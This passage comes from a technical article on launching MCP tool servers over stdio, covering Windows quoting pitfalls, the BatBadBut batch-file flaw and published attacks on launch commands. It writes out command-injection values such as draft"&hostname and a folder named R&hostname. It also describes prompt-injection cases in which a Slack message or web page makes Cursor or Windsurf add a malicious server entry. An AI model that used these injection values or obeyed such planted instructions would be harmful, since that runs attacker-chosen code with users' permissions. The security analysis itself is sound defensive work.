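### A shell between the host and the server

When a wrapper starts notes-server in the ordinary way, the shell waits for it to finish. The shell is then the host application's child process, and notes-server is the shell's child. Messages are unaffected because notes-server inherits the shell's input and output, but the extra process matters when the host tries to stop the server.

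The stdio rules recommend that the host close the server's input, wait for the server to exit, and use force only if it doesn't. Closing the input works through a wrapper because notes-server shares that input and can detect when it closes. On Linux and macOS, Claude Code sends an interrupt signal, a termination signal 100 milliseconds later if the process is still running, and a kill signal after another 400 milliseconds. These signals are less reliable than closing the input. If they go only to the shell, they can end it and leave notes-server running without a parent, and a kill signal ends the shell before it can pass anything on.

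The `exec` in the earlier wrappers prevents this by replacing the shell with notes-server in the same process, so the host's signals reach the server directly. Some shells do this automatically when the command string is a single simple command, but a wrapper that has to work on different machines shouldn't depend on it.

Leftover servers can pile up quickly. In *MCP Process Leak / Orphaned Children on Restart*, Aniket_B counted 7 orphaned processes that Cursor had started after one restart and 42 after the fifth. According to a reply on Cursor's forum, this was a known issue, and the editor wasn't properly terminating servers when a user reloaded the window or restarted. The fault was in the host, so removing a shell from the launch entries wouldn't necessarily have fixed it.

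`exec` doesn't help with layers below the shell. `exec npx -y notes-server` replaces the shell with `npx`, but `npx` may start other processes. The host can solve this more completely by starting each server in a separate process group and sending signals to the whole group. The signals then reach the shell, the package runner and the server, except any that have moved to another group.

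## Why are launches on Windows harder to get right?

According to Microsoft's *Everyone quotes command line arguments the wrong way*, Windows keeps only one command-line string for each process. On Linux, `execve` gives a new program an array of arguments instead. A Windows host application that holds a list of arguments must therefore join them into one string, and the launch works only if the new program splits that string by the same rules.

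### Joining and splitting

Most Windows programs split the line by the rules of Microsoft's C runtime, which the documentation for Python sets out:

- A space or tab ends an argument, unless it is inside double quotes.
- A backslash directly before a double quote makes the quote an ordinary character.
- Two backslashes directly before a double quote count as one.
- Any other backslash is an ordinary character.

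The last rule lets paths such as `C:\Hello there.txt`, an example from Microsoft's *What's up with the strange treatment of quotation marks and backslashes* (2010), come through unchanged. But a path that ends in a backslash causes trouble if the host application simply puts quotes around it:

```
notes-server.exe "C:\R&D notes\" --writable
```

Here notes-server reads `\"` as a literal quotation mark and receives a single argument, `C:\R&D notes" --writable`. Correct joining code would have doubled the final backslash. Some libraries don't quote arguments at all. Microsoft's C functions for starting programs, the `_spawn` and `_exec` families, only put spaces between the arguments, so a folder name containing a space is split into several arguments.

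If the joining code is correct and notes-server is an `.exe` file, Ana's folder arrives intact:

```
launch entry   "args": ["C:\\R&D notes"]
command line   notes-server.exe "C:\R&D notes"
argv[1]        C:\R&D notes
```

An ampersand doesn't need escaping when a program is launched without the command interpreter, and escaping it causes errors. Microsoft's *If you're not using the command line interpreter* (2013) describes a customer who put a caret before an ampersand, as one would at a command prompt, but passed the line straight to CreateProcess, the Windows function that starts a program. The program started but couldn't find the registry key named in the command, because the caret had become part of the name.

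Windows can also misread the program's own path if it contains a space. If a host application passes `C:\Program Files\Notes\notes-server.exe` to CreateProcess without quotes, Windows tries `C:\Program.exe` first. *When spaces break your CreateProcess (and how to fix it)* (2025) explains how an attacker could place a program at the shortened path. The safest of its fixes is to pass the program's path as a separate value, which Windows doesn't split.

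### How cmd.exe reads the same line

A POSIX shell splits a command line into an argument array, but cmd.exe edits the line as text and leaves the next program to split it. The table compares cmd.exe's rules with those of the C runtime.

| Text | C runtime | cmd.exe |
|---|---|---|
| `"` | Starts or ends a quoted part | Starts or ends a quoted part |
| `\"` | An ordinary quotation mark | A backslash, then a `"` that starts or ends a quoted part |
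| `&` | Ordinary | Ends a command, unless quoted |
| `^` | Ordinary | Makes the next character ordinary, unless quoted |
| `%NAME%` | Ordinary | Becomes the variable's value, even inside quotes |
| `'` | Ordinary | Ordinary |

The C runtime's rules and cmd.exe's rules treat `\"` differently, which is enough to allow command injection. Suppose a host application passes on the search term `draft"&hostname`. Correct joining code turns it into `"draft\"&hostname"`, and a program that follows the C runtime's rules recovers the original term. But cmd.exe ends the quoted part at the second quotation mark, treats the ampersand as an operator and runs `hostname`, a utility that prints the computer's name. A folder name can't cause this, because Windows doesn't allow double quotes in file names.

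Percent signs are harder to handle because cmd.exe has no equivalent of the single quotes that preserve every character in a POSIX shell. A folder named `%OS% notes` reaches the program as `Windows_NT notes` even if the host application has quoted it.

cmd.exe also fills in variables before it looks for operators, the reverse of the POSIX order. If `NOTES_DIR` holds `C:\R&D`, an unquoted `%NOTES_DIR%` therefore becomes two commands. Letting the shell fill in the variable was the safer choice on Linux, but it gives much less protection here.

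### Why npx fails to start

In a bug report that Good First Issue lists, a Windows 11 user couldn't start a tool server because the host application reported that `npx` was not in the system path. But `npx` worked in both of the user's terminals, and the command `where npx` found two files:

```
D:\nodejs\npx
D:\nodejs\npx.cmd
```

`npx` is a script for Unix-like shells, and `npx.cmd` is a batch file. When the user changed `npx` to `npx.cmd` in the launch entry, the server started.

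A terminal finds the batch file by trying the file endings listed in the `PATHEXT` variable, which include `.cmd`. Programming languages often search differently. The source code of Rust, the language of several coding agents, adds only `.exe` to a name that has no ending, so it looks for `npx.exe` when given `npx`. A contributor with the username 25621 (2025) gave this as the reason OpenAI's coding agent Codex reported "program not found" for `npx`, `pnpm` and `yarn`.

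A launch can involve a batch file even without a package runner. When npm, the package manager that comes with Node.js, installs a package on Windows, it creates a `.cmd` file for the package's command. If Ana installed notes-server with npm, `notes-server` is also a batch file.

### The cmd /c remedy

The usual remedy is to start cmd.exe and have it find the batch file. Spring AI's *docs(mcp): add Windows STDIO configuration guidance*, written for a Java framework, recommends this for `npx` and other batch files. Ana's entry would be:

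```json
{ "command": "cmd", "args": ["/c", "npx", "-y", "notes-server", "C:\\R&D"] }
```

As in a launch through cross-spawn, three parsers read the folder's name before `npx` can use it: cmd.exe on the line after `/c`, cmd.exe again inside `npx.cmd`, which inserts the arguments into a line of its own, and then Node.js. (And `npx` still has to start notes-server, which can add more.)

cmd.exe would read the name twice even without the wrapper. In *subprocess.Popen on a Windows batch file always acts as if shell=True*, the Python developer Sun explains that CreateProcess runs a batch file by putting `%ComSpec% /c` in front of the line, and `ComSpec` normally points to cmd.exe. An entry that names `npx.cmd` therefore gets the same three readings. The wrapper just makes the shell visible.

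Whether Ana's folder survives depends on how the host application joined the line. Microsoft's published joining function adds quotes only if an argument is empty or contains a space, a tab, a line break or a double quote. An ampersand isn't on the list, so these are the lines for two possible folders:

```
C:\R&D          cmd /c npx -y notes-server C:\R&D
C:\R&D notes    cmd /c npx -y notes-server "C:\R&D notes"
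```

The longer name works because the quotes added for its space also protect the ampersand, and they stay in place when cmd.exe reads the line inside `npx.cmd`. The shorter name has no quotes, so cmd.exe starts the server on `C:\R` and then tries to run a program called `D`.

abigail (2018) reported the same behaviour in Python. An `.exe` file received the arguments `foo`, `&&`, `echo` and `%PROGRAMFILES%` unchanged. When a batch file took the `.exe` file's place, it received only `foo`, after which cmd.exe ran `echo` and printed `C:\Program Files`. None of those arguments contains a space, so Python had added no quotes.

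People often fix launch problems by removing the spaces from folder names, but on Windows this can cause the failure it is meant to prevent. If Ana renames her folder `R&D-notes`, the path is no longer quoted, so cmd.exe treats the `&` as a command separator and looks for a program called `D-notes`. A malicious colleague could use the same behavior to run `hostname` by naming a shared folder `R&hostname`. The name `R&echo notes` wouldn't run anything, because its space causes the path to be quoted.

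The broken launch can also appear to work. cmd.exe runs the commands on either side of an ampersand one after the other, so notes-server starts on `C:\R` and keeps its input. A POSIX shell would have cut that input off. If a folder named `C:\R` exists, the model reads the wrong files, and the error about `D` appears only after the server exits.

Ana might try to protect the ampersand herself by editing the string in `args`:

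| String in `args`, after JSON decoding | Result |
|---|---|
| `"C:\R&D"` | Breaks. The host writes `"\"C:\R&D\""`, and cmd.exe finds the ampersand outside the quotes |
| `C:\R^&D` | Breaks. The first reading removes the caret, and the second splits the line |
| `C:\R^^^&D` | Works. The first reading leaves `C:\R^&D`, and the second leaves `C:\R&D` |

Three carets are correct only if cmd.exe parses the line exactly twice. If the command later becomes an `.exe` behind the same `cmd /c`, cmd.exe parses the line only once, leaving one caret, and notes-server will look for a folder named `R^&D`.

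### 'C:\Program' is not recognized

Node.js normally installs itself under `C:\Program Files`, so an entry that gives the full path of `npx.cmd` contains a space before any folder comes into it. Node.js' *Child process* tells developers to quote a batch file's name if it contains spaces. If the host application doesn't, cmd.exe takes everything before the space as the command and prints an error that begins:

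```
'C:\Program' is not recognized
```

The message can also appear when both paths have quotes:

```
cmd /c "C:\Program Files\nodejs\npx.cmd" -y notes-server "C:\R&D notes"
```

This comes from a rule described in cmd.exe's built-in help. If the text after `/c` starts with a quotation mark, cmd.exe normally removes that mark and the last one on the line. It keeps them if there are exactly two marks and they enclose the name of an existing program, with no ampersand or similar character in it. So the entry works with a folder named `C:\notes`, which needs no quotes. `C:\R&D notes` does need them, which brings the total to four marks, so cmd.exe removes the first and last and the program's path is no longer properly quoted. The program's name appears in the error message even though only the folder changed. Writing plain `npx` avoids this because the text after `/c` then doesn't start with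 a quotation mark.

### BatBadBut

On 9 April 2024, the maintainers of several programming languages published security notices about batch files. *BatBadBut* (RyotaK, 2024) explains the flaw behind them. Most languages have a function that runs a program with a list of arguments, and the documentation often says that no shell will interpret the list. But if the program was a batch file, Windows started cmd.exe anyway. These functions escaped double quotes with a backslash, which cmd.exe doesn't recognise as an escape, so an argument like `"&hostname` ran `hostname` as a command. In Node.js this happened even with the shell option off.

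Six years earlier, abigail had described the behaviour for Python, and CERT/CC's *Multiple programming languages fail to escape arguments properly in Microsoft Windows* notes that Microsoft had documented some of the concerns by 2011. CreateProcess starts cmd.exe only for batch files, although CERT/CC's wording could suggest that it does so for every command.

Escaping quotation marks correctly for cmd.exe isn't enough to prevent command injection. The variable `CMDCMDLINE` holds the command line that started cmd.exe, which may end in a quotation mark. An attacker can include an expression in an argument that extracts this last character. Because cmd.exe fills in variables before it interprets quotation marks, the extracted mark closes the quoted part, even though the argument contained no quotation mark when the program checked it.

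RyotaK's recipe therefore also replaces each percent sign with `%%cd:~,%`. The part after the first percent sign expands to nothing and stops cmd.exe from recognising a variable's name. The recipe also doubles the quotation marks, removes line breaks and depends on two cmd.exe settings. In RyotaK's tests, the recipe prevented injection, but RyotaK wasn't sure that it was the best method.

The nine languages in RyotaK's list responded in three ways:

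| Response | Languages |
|---|---|
| Changed the code | Haskell, Node.js, PHP, Rust |
| Changed the documentation | Erlang, Go, Python, Ruby |
| Declined to fix it | Java |

To keep its guarantee that arguments arrive unchanged, Rust sometimes refuses to start the program. Albini (2024), in *CVE-2024-24576*, wrote that the developers had found no way of escaping arguments that was always correct. Since version 1.77.2, Rust escapes the arguments it can and returns an `InvalidInput` error for the rest. Tenable's *CVE-2024-24576* adds that the new code is cautious and could reject valid arguments.

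Node.js did not attempt escaping. *Wednesday, April 10, 2024 Security Releases* (Gonzaga, 2024) announced a breaking change to the Node.js `spawn` function, which now fails with the error `EINVAL` if a program passes it a `.bat` or `.cmd` file without setting the shell option.

Both fixes had gaps at first, because recognising a batch file is difficult. Windows ignores spaces and full stops at the end of a file name, so it treats `.bat. .` as `.bat`, but Rust's check looked only at the last letters. *Security advisory for the standard library (CVE-2024-43402)* (Albini, 2024) announced a correction in Rust 1.81.0 and rated the severity as low. Rust's current code gets the full path from Windows before checking the ending. Mondoo's *CVE-2024-36138* records a similar bypass of the first Node.js fix.

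Python's developers didn't consider it a flaw in Python. zooba (2024) argued that the operating system starts cmd.exe intentionally, and that an attacker who can influence both the program and its arguments can already exploit the application. The second argument holds for someone who controls the launch command, but it doesn't cover a colleague who can only name a folder because the launch entry's owner has already chosen `npx` as the program.

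The flaw's severity depends on the application. Albini rated it critical for programs that pass untrusted arguments to batch files, while RyotaK thought most applications were unaffected and warned against applying a library's severity score directly to the applications that use it. Applications that launch tool servers are more exposed than most because `npx` is a batch file on every ordinary Windows installation, but an attacker still needs to influence an argument.

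### The Node.js shell option

The Node.js fix left developers with a launch that no longer worked and an error that went away when they set `shell: true`, as VS Code's team advised. But Node.js doesn't quote arguments when the option is on, so both of Ana's folders break:

```
npx -y notes-server C:\R&D
npx -y notes-server C:\R&D notes
```

So a change meant to stop command injection encouraged people to use a setting that makes injection easier. But the old behaviour was dangerous without any warning, and a developer who types `shell: true` at least has a chance to notice that a shell is involved.

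The Node.js 26 documentation still lists the `shell` option as one way to start a batch file, but marks it "not recommended, see DEP0190". DEP0190 deprecates passing an argument array together with the `shell` option, and Node.js 24 prints a warning when a program does this. Like the `shell` option, the other two documented methods involve `cmd.exe`. One is `exec`, which takes a single string that the developer must quote, and the other is starting `cmd.exe` directly with `/c`.

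Timeless0911 (2026), *fix*, changed a JavaScript project to call `cmd.exe /c` on Windows instead of setting `shell: true`. This removes the warning and restores ordinary quoting, so `C:\R&D notes` would be passed correctly, but `C:\R&D` would still break, now without a warning.

Python's documentation, by contrast, suggests `shell=True` for batch files with untrusted arguments, so that Python can escape special characters. That is hard to reconcile with the paragraph before it, which makes the application responsible for all quoting when `shell=True` is set. Sun thought running a batch file directly carries the same risks as `shell=True`. Developers shouldn't treat `shell=True` as a fix in either language.

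### What the official kits do

The TypeScript kit relies on cross-spawn for quoting. This library calls cmd.exe for anything other than an `.exe` or `.com` file. It quotes every argument, even those without spaces, and then puts carets before the special characters. With a plain `npx` entry, both of Ana's folders arrive intact.

The usual remedy, launching the server through `cmd /c`, undoes this. If `command` is `cmd`, cross-spawn finds `cmd.exe`, an ordinary `.exe` file, and does no escaping. Node.js then joins the arguments into a command line by the common rule, and `C:\R&D` breaks. In this kit, changing an entry from `npx` to `cmd /c npx` to make it work on Windows therefore makes it less safe.

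Cross-spawn's maintainers describe its handling of Windows as correct in the copy of their introduction that Chromium keeps. Values that contain double quotes are still worth testing, because they need escaping twice if cmd.exe reads them twice. The batch-file problem described on cross-spawn's npm page concerns files in `node_modules/.bin`, but the `npx.cmd` in the bug report was in `D:\nodejs`.

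The Python kit finds the batch file but adds no protection against the way cmd.exe parses arguments. In Model Context Protocol's *utilities*, the launch code resolves `npx` to the path of `npx.cmd`. Python then joins the path and arguments by the C runtime's rules, and Windows starts cmd.exe to run the file. BatBadBut describes this situation.

With the Rust kit, the host application builds the command itself. *Windows Path Resolution Problem in tokio::process::Command* reports that plain `npx` fails on Windows and proposes a helper that looks up the full path first. Given the full path, Rust recognises the batch file and either applies its own escaping or returns an error.

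| Launch on Windows | `C:\R&D` | `C:\R&D notes` |
|---|---|---|
| `notes-server.exe`, started directly | Intact | Intact |
| `npx` in the TypeScript kit | Intact | Intact |
| `cmd /c npx` in the TypeScript kit | Cut to `C:\R` | Intact |
| `npx` in the Python kit | Cut to `C:\R` | Intact |
| Full path of `npx.cmd` in the Rust kit | Intact | Intact |
| `npx` through Node's shell option | Cut to `C:\R` | Cut to `C:\R` |

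Batch files also leave more processes to clean up, because cmd.exe and Node.js both sit between the host application and the server. On Windows, Claude Code closes the server's input, waits 300 milliseconds and then ends the whole tree of processes. The Python kit puts the process it starts into a job object, a Windows group whose members can be ended together. But it does so just after the launch, so any child process that starts before then stays outside the group, according to a comment in the code.

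## How do attackers gain control of a launch command?

Most launch attacks that researchers reported in 2025 and 2026 did not require a quoting error. The attacker wrote or changed a launch entry, and the host application ran it as written, so neither correct quoting nor direct invocation would have stopped the attack.

Cantina's *how Anthropic's MCP stdio model turns configuration into code execution* lists three conditions for an attack through a launch command: the host application accepts a command, arguments, environment variables or a working directory; untrusted text can reach those fields; and the host runs the result with useful privileges. Any host that supports local servers meets the first condition and usually the third, so the risk depends mostly on who can write to those fields. On a hosted platform, that may be any visitor to the website. On a developer's laptop, it may be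 a colleague, a stranger who publishes a tool server, or the agent itself after it has read a malicious message.

### Users of a hosted platform

Some organisations run an agent platform on their own servers and let people configure it through a web page. If a user adds a tool server that uses the stdio transport, the tool server's process starts on the organisation's machine.

WeKnora, Tencent's platform for asking questions about collections of documents, had a simple version of this flaw. According to GitHub's *Command Injection in (MCP stdio test) in Tencent/WeKnora* (2026), any logged-in user could send the platform a launch entry. A harmless one would look like this:

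```json
{
  "name": "notes",
  "transport_type": "stdio",
  "stdio_config": { "command": "date", "args": [] }
}
```

WeKnora saved the entry in its database without checking it. When the user then asked to test the connection, WeKnora loaded the entry and started the program. In this example, `date` would run before the test failed.

The process ran with the platform's permissions, so it could read configuration files, keys and environment variables. Several customers can share one WeKnora installation, and according to the advisory, an attack might reach other customers' data, depending on the setup.

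GitHub classifies the flaw, CVE-2026-22688, as a failure to neutralise special characters in a command, but the entry above has none. The published demonstration used `bash` only because the attacker chose it as the program. WeKnora had neither an allowlist of programs nor a rule that only administrators could add local servers. The advisory lists versions before 0.2.5 as affected.

Letta AI, a platform for agents with long-term memory, listed only two remote transports in the connection form on its web page. Researchers at OX Security read the source code and found that the server also accepted the stdio transport. They pressed "Test connection", intercepted the outgoing request and replaced the remote configuration with a launch entry. Its command ran on Letta AI's production servers.

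Any logged-in user can carry out this attack by altering the requests that their own browser sends, so removing an option from the form gives no protection unless the server also refuses that option. OX Security calls this a simulated man-in-the-middle attack, but the attacker does not have to get between a victim and the server.

Langflow, an open-source tool for building AI agents, didn't require an account. Its settings accepted stdio entries, and anyone who opened the web page or sent a simple request received a session token, the credential that identifies a logged-in user. A second request with that token and a stdio entry started the attacker's program. OX Security used Shodan, a search engine for internet-connected devices, to find over 915 visible Langflow instances, though some may have had other protection. The researchers reported the flaw on 11 January 2026 and received a direct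 acknowledgement on 18 March.

IBM, which owns Langflow, listed seven more flaws in July 2026 in *Langflow is affected by security vulnerabilities in Model Context Protocol features*. One (CVE-2026-17623) let a user with an ordinary account run commands because Langflow didn't properly validate the `command` field. IBM rated its severity 8.8 out of 10. Another (CVE-2026-9077) let such a user, working through the web platform, write launch entries into the configuration files of code editors on the machine running Langflow, even though Langflow was supposed to accept those changes only from the machine itself. Version 1.11.0 fixed all seven flaws.

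### MCP's part in the October 2026 Langflow flaws

IBM published another Langflow bulletin on 28 October 2026. According to The Hacker News' *Critical Langflow Flaws Could Let Unauthenticated Attackers Run Code on Servers* (2026), it covers four flaws in every release from 1.0.0 to 1.12.8. Attackers can exploit two without an account, and both have a severity score of 9.8. One lets them bypass authentication and the other lets them run arbitrary code. IBM described one of the four as "exploitable through model context protocol tool enumeration", which sounds like another attack through a malicious launch entry.

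But in this case Langflow was acting as the tool server. It can offer its workflows as tools to other AI applications, and tool enumeration is a request for the list of those tools. Trent (2026), in *MCP as the New Attack Surface*, describes the attack in three steps:

1. Someone without an account sends a request to Langflow's automatic login address, which returns a session with full administrator rights.
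2. The attacker uses that session to reach Langflow's MCP address and list the tools, which include tools for creating and running workflows.
3. The attacker creates a workflow that contains Python code, and Langflow runs it.

In this attack, the attacker used MCP to reach a feature that already ran code, and automatic login gave them permission to use it. Nobody wrote a launch entry, and no host application started a local server.

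The third step has less public evidence than the first two. A module for Metasploit, a widely used toolkit for testing attacks, connects to Langflow's MCP address without credentials and lists the tools, but it doesn't run any code. Trent calls code execution "the logical next step". The module's author tested it on version 1.8.4 with automatic login turned on. The Hacker News notes that IBM's bulletin does not specify whether servers with automatic login turned off are vulnerable.

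Automatic login had caused a similar problem in July. Intruder's *CVE-2026-9103* (2026) explains that automatic login gave administrator tokens to any caller, which attackers could combine with a separate flaw to run code. The US cybersecurity agency CISA added that combination to its catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities in August. IBM's earlier fixes made the tokens expire sooner, but Langflow still gave them to anonymous callers. Version 1.13.0 turns automatic login off by default. An administrator who had blocked every stdio entry would still have needed this upgrade. As of 30 October, neither of the two critical flaws was in CISA's catalogue.

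### People who can change a shared project

Developers share code through repositories, and many host applications read launch entries from a file inside the project. Anyone who can change that file can write a launch entry for everyone else who opens the project.

Cursor asked its users to approve each new entry, but this protection had a gap. Suppose a colleague adds an entry called "notes" to a project, and Ana approves it. A week later the colleague changes the command:

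```
approved   "notes": { "command": "notes-server", "args": ["."] }
changed    "notes": { "command": "date", "args": [] }
```

Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu (2025) found in *CVE-2025-54136* that Cursor tied the approval to the entry's name, so it would run `date` without asking each time Ana opened the project. In their demonstration at the security company Check Point, they used the changed entry to take remote control of the victim's computer. The new command had the developer's permissions, which often cover source code and cloud credentials.

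The attacker needs more access here than on Langflow. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2025-54136* (2025), the attacker must be able to change a branch that the victim uses or write files on the victim's machine. Such an attacker could be a colleague or someone who has stolen a colleague's account.

Check Point reported the flaw on 16 July 2025, and Cursor released version 1.3 on 29 July. The release notes didn't specifically mention the flaw, but Charikov and colleagues tested the new version and found that any change to an entry, even an added space, now brings up the approval prompt.

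This fix can't detect a change to a file that the entry points to. If Ana approves an entry that runs a script in the project, a colleague can rewrite the script without changing the entry. A package runner creates the same problem if the entry doesn't pin a version, because the publisher can release a new one.

Claude Code has a similar weakness. The security researcher felixbillieres found that when a user approves a server, Claude Code stores the server's name and never checks its command again. The proposed fix is to store a hash, a short fingerprint of the configuration, and ask again if it changes. Anthropic holds that someone who approves a project trusts its files. Mindgard's *Approve Once, Exploit Forever* describes the same problem with whole folders in Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI. After the user approves a folder, the agent doesn't ask again when the folder's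 configuration changes.

An attacker could also exploit Claude Code without an earlier approval. Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026), in *Caught in the Hook*, reported that a malicious repository could run commands on the computer of a developer who cloned and opened it. One of the flaws, CVE-2025-59536, involved the `enableAllProjectMcpServers` setting, according to BeyondMachines. This setting approves every tool server that a project defines, and the project's own files could turn it on, so an attacker could supply both the launch entry and its approval.

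ThaiCERT's *Critical Vulnerabilities in Claude Code Could Enable Remote Code Execution* lists two related flaws. One bypassed consent through another project settings file. The other, CVE-2026-21852, let a project change the address to which Claude Code sent its requests, so the user's API key could go to an attacker's server without the exploit starting a process. Anthropic has patched both.

A project can still start its own tool servers once the user trusts the folder. Adversa AI found that Claude Code, Gemini CLI, Cursor CLI and Copilot CLI start these servers immediately after the user accepts the trust prompt. In all four, "yes" is the default answer, so pressing Enter is enough. Datadog Security Labs found the same behaviour in Codex, which starts the server before the user or the agent tries to use it.

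Help Net Security's *One keypress is all it takes to compromise four AI coding tools* describes an attack that takes two small files. One defines a server with an ordinary name such as "linter", and the other approves it. Claude Code prompts the user to confirm that they created or trust the project. An earlier version included an explicit warning that the project could run code through MCP, which gave a cautious user a reason to check the launch entries before answering.

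A build server may have nobody present to answer the prompt. In a summary on GitHub, Adversa AI reports that the attack needs no keypress when Claude Code runs in an automated build, and that Anthropic regards the behaviour as intended. Adversa AI argues that the problem can't be reported to a single vendor because it is a convention that several products share. Until the prompts change, the practical protection is to read a project's configuration before trusting its folder, and to keep automated agents away from code submitted by strangers.

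### Agents that edit their own configuration

Many coding agents can write files, which may include the file that holds their launch entries. If so, an attacker can change those entries through prompt injection, which means placing text in material the model reads so that the model follows it as an instruction. The attacker doesn't need an account on the victim's machine or access to the repository, only a way to get the model to read the text.

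SC Media describes a demonstration by the security company Aim Labs in which an attacker posts a message in a public channel on Slack, a workplace chat service. The message contains instructions for the agent to "improve" `mcp.json`, Cursor's launch configuration, by adding a new entry. When the user asks Cursor to summarise recent messages, Cursor follows these instructions. It saves the edit before the user accepts or rejects it, so the command runs even if the user rejects the edit.

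Tenable's *CVE-2025-54135* (2025) describes a narrower gap in which Cursor asked for approval before the agent edited an existing dotfile, but not before it created one. A dotfile is a configuration file whose name begins with a dot, and Cursor also counts those inside folders like `.cursor`. A project with no MCP configuration file was the easier target, because the agent could create one without approval. GCVE's *CVE-2025-54135* (2025) links the flaw to Cursor's advisory, GHSA-4cxx-hrm3-49rm. In that advisory, which SecurityWeek quotes, Cursor acknowledged that an attacker could use the configuration file to add a new MCP server and run code directly.

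Cursor's fix stopped the agent from writing sensitive MCP files without approval. SC Media gives the fixed version as 1.3, and Tenable gives it as 1.3.9. But according to NVD's *CVE-2025-59944*, the file name check was case-sensitive in versions up to 1.6.23. Windows and macOS normally treat `mcp.json` and `MCP.json` as the same file, so a write using different capitalization could bypass the check and still change the configuration.

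Tenable reports that attackers had not exploited either of the 2025 flaws, the Slack attack or the changed approval, before their disclosure.

OX Security demonstrated a similar attack on the code editor Windsurf (CVE-2026-30615). The victim visits the attacker's website and copies a prompt that looks legitimate. When Windsurf requests the same site, the site returns different content containing a hidden instruction. Windsurf then changes its `mcp.json` without showing the user the change, and the new entry runs immediately with the user's permissions.

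The victim has to visit the site and copy the prompt, but never gets a chance to refuse the new entry. OX Security calls this a "zero-click" attack and says Windsurf was the only editor it tested where the attack needed no user interaction, but only the last stage needs none. When OX Security published its findings, it listed the flaw as reported but unpatched.

### Install links and registries

A user can also install an attacker's launch entry directly. Some host applications accept one-click install links, which pass the application a ready-made entry from a web page. The link's author chooses the command, so Ana might click "Install notes-server" and receive an entry that runs `date` with her permissions.

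For this case, the protocol's consent rule requires the host to show the full command. Cantina traces the rule to the SEP-1024 proposal and says the host must also identify the step as potentially dangerous. Ana would probably notice `date`, but she could easily miss a package name that differs from the real one by a letter.

Registries, which are public catalogues of tool servers, create a similar risk on a larger scale. OX Security submitted a malicious test entry to 11 registries, and nine accepted it. For an attack to succeed, a user would still have to find and install the server, and the host application would have to start it. SecurityWeek's *‘By Design’ Flaw in MCP Could Enable Widespread AI Supply Chain Attacks* names GitHub's installation process as an exception, which suggests that checks at this stage are practical.

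A launch entry from a registry, such as `npx -y notes-server`, may look normal even if the package is malicious. Checking the entry for strange symbols or unexpected programs would miss this attack, so the check has to cover the package and its publisher.

### What OX Security tested and what it estimated

The registry test and the attacks on Letta AI, Langflow and Windsurf come from an April 2026 OX Security study. The researchers looked for products that passed outside input to the launch functions of the official MCP kits. They then worked out how each product handled configuration, and either added a stdio server directly or changed a network request. They ran commands on six live platforms with real users.

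The study led to more than 30 disclosures. OX Security lists ten products with vulnerability numbers:

| Product | How the attacker reached the launch | Status in April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| GPT Researcher | Web interface | Reported |
| LiteLLM | JSON configuration, with an account | Patched |
| Agent Zero | Web interface, no account | Reported |
| Fay Framework | Web interface, no account | Reported |
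| Bisheng | Web interface, with an account that anyone could register | Patched |
| Langchain-Chatchat | Web interface, no account | Reported |
| Jaaz | Web interface, no account | Reported |
| Upsonic | Extra arguments to a permitted package runner | Warning issued |
| Windsurf | Prompt injection | Reported |
| DocsGPT | Network request changed to select stdio | Patched |

None of these descriptions involves a quoting error. The list of ten products gives Bisheng and Jaaz the same number, CVE-2026-33224, and one of the two entries is probably a misprint. The list also shows only three patches, whereas SecurityWeek reported more than ten patched vulnerabilities.

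The study's best-known figures, over 150 million downloads and up to 200,000 vulnerable instances, are much larger. OX Security did not test anything on that scale. The download figure counts copies of the affected software, not users, and includes copies that an attacker cannot reach. For example, if Ana's editor uses an official kit but only Ana can write its launch entries, her copy is counted even though it gives no one else control of the launch.

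The 200,000 figure is an upper estimate. OX Security counted over 7,000 publicly accessible servers and doesn't explain in its announcement how it got from that count to 200,000. The 7,000 are servers the researchers could see, not ones on which they ran commands.

The smaller numbers are better evidence. The six live platforms and ten named products show that separate development teams made the same mistake, but not how common it is, because the counts include only products that failed. The registry result gives a proportion, 9 of 11, but from a small sample.

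### How threat taxonomies classify these attacks

Researchers have also tried to list the threats to MCP systematically, but control of the launch command fits awkwardly into their lists. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) defines 38 threats. Its "command injection" category covers model output that reaches a shell through a tool after the server has started. "Insecure stdio descriptor handling" concerns a process that reads or tampers with the messages between client and server, rather than the command that launches the server.

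Two other categories fit better. "Supply chain compromise" covers a malicious package in a registry. "Missing integrity verification" covers software that changes after the user has authorised it, which resembles the changed Cursor entry. However, its definition refers to the tool's description and code, not the launch command. The table of definitions has no separate category for an attacker who chooses the program in a launch entry, as on WeKnora. Shen and colleagues kept only threats with documented evidence, but there was evidence for this one, since the Cursor flaws had been public for seven months when the taxonomy appeared in March 2026.

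*MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) sorts 49 attacks by the part of the system that could first stop them. It lists "Command Execution" under the client and its software development kit, and "Persistence via Host Auto-Launch" under the host application. The second name fits the Cursor attack because the changed command ran each time the victim opened the project.

This division is useful because the two layers have different information. A software kit can refuse to start a program that isn't on an allowlist, but it can't check whether Ana approved the same entry last week. The host application can check this if it keeps a record of the whole entry. Rostamzadeh and colleagues also compared 13 defensive products and found that only one covered command execution. They judged coverage from each product's design without running attacks, so even that product may not stop a malicious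 launch in practice.

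## Can a platform safely accept launch commands from its users?

A shared platform could avoid attacks like the one on WeKnora by refusing all user-submitted launch entries, but users could then no longer add their own tool servers. Several platforms instead accept the entries after checking them. In 2025 and 2026, researchers repeatedly got past these checks, usually with entries that looked ordinary.

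### Removing special characters

The simplest check looks for characters that have a special meaning to a shell, such as `&`, `;`, `|` and `$`, and either deletes them or refuses the entry. This makes sense if the platform inserts the text into a shell command. But with the official Python and TypeScript kits on Linux or macOS, there's no shell to misread an ampersand, so the filter removes a danger that wasn't there. It also leaves the user free to choose the program:

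```json
{ "command": "date", "args": [] }
```

This entry contains nothing to filter. Neither would `sh` with the arguments `-c` and `date`, even though that launch does involve a shell.

The filter also causes problems for Ana. If it rejects ampersands, she can't open "R&D notes". If it deletes them, notes-server looks for a folder called "RD notes", which may not exist or may be a different folder. Rejecting them is better because she at least gets an error message.

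A filter is more useful on Windows, where cmd.exe often parses the arguments to `npx`. It could stop a folder named `R&hostname` from running `hostname`, but it wouldn't stop someone from naming `hostname` as the program to launch.

### Allowing only certain programs

An allowlist of program names blocks `date` directly. Flowise, an open-source platform for building AI agents in a visual editor, shows how much protection such a list provides.

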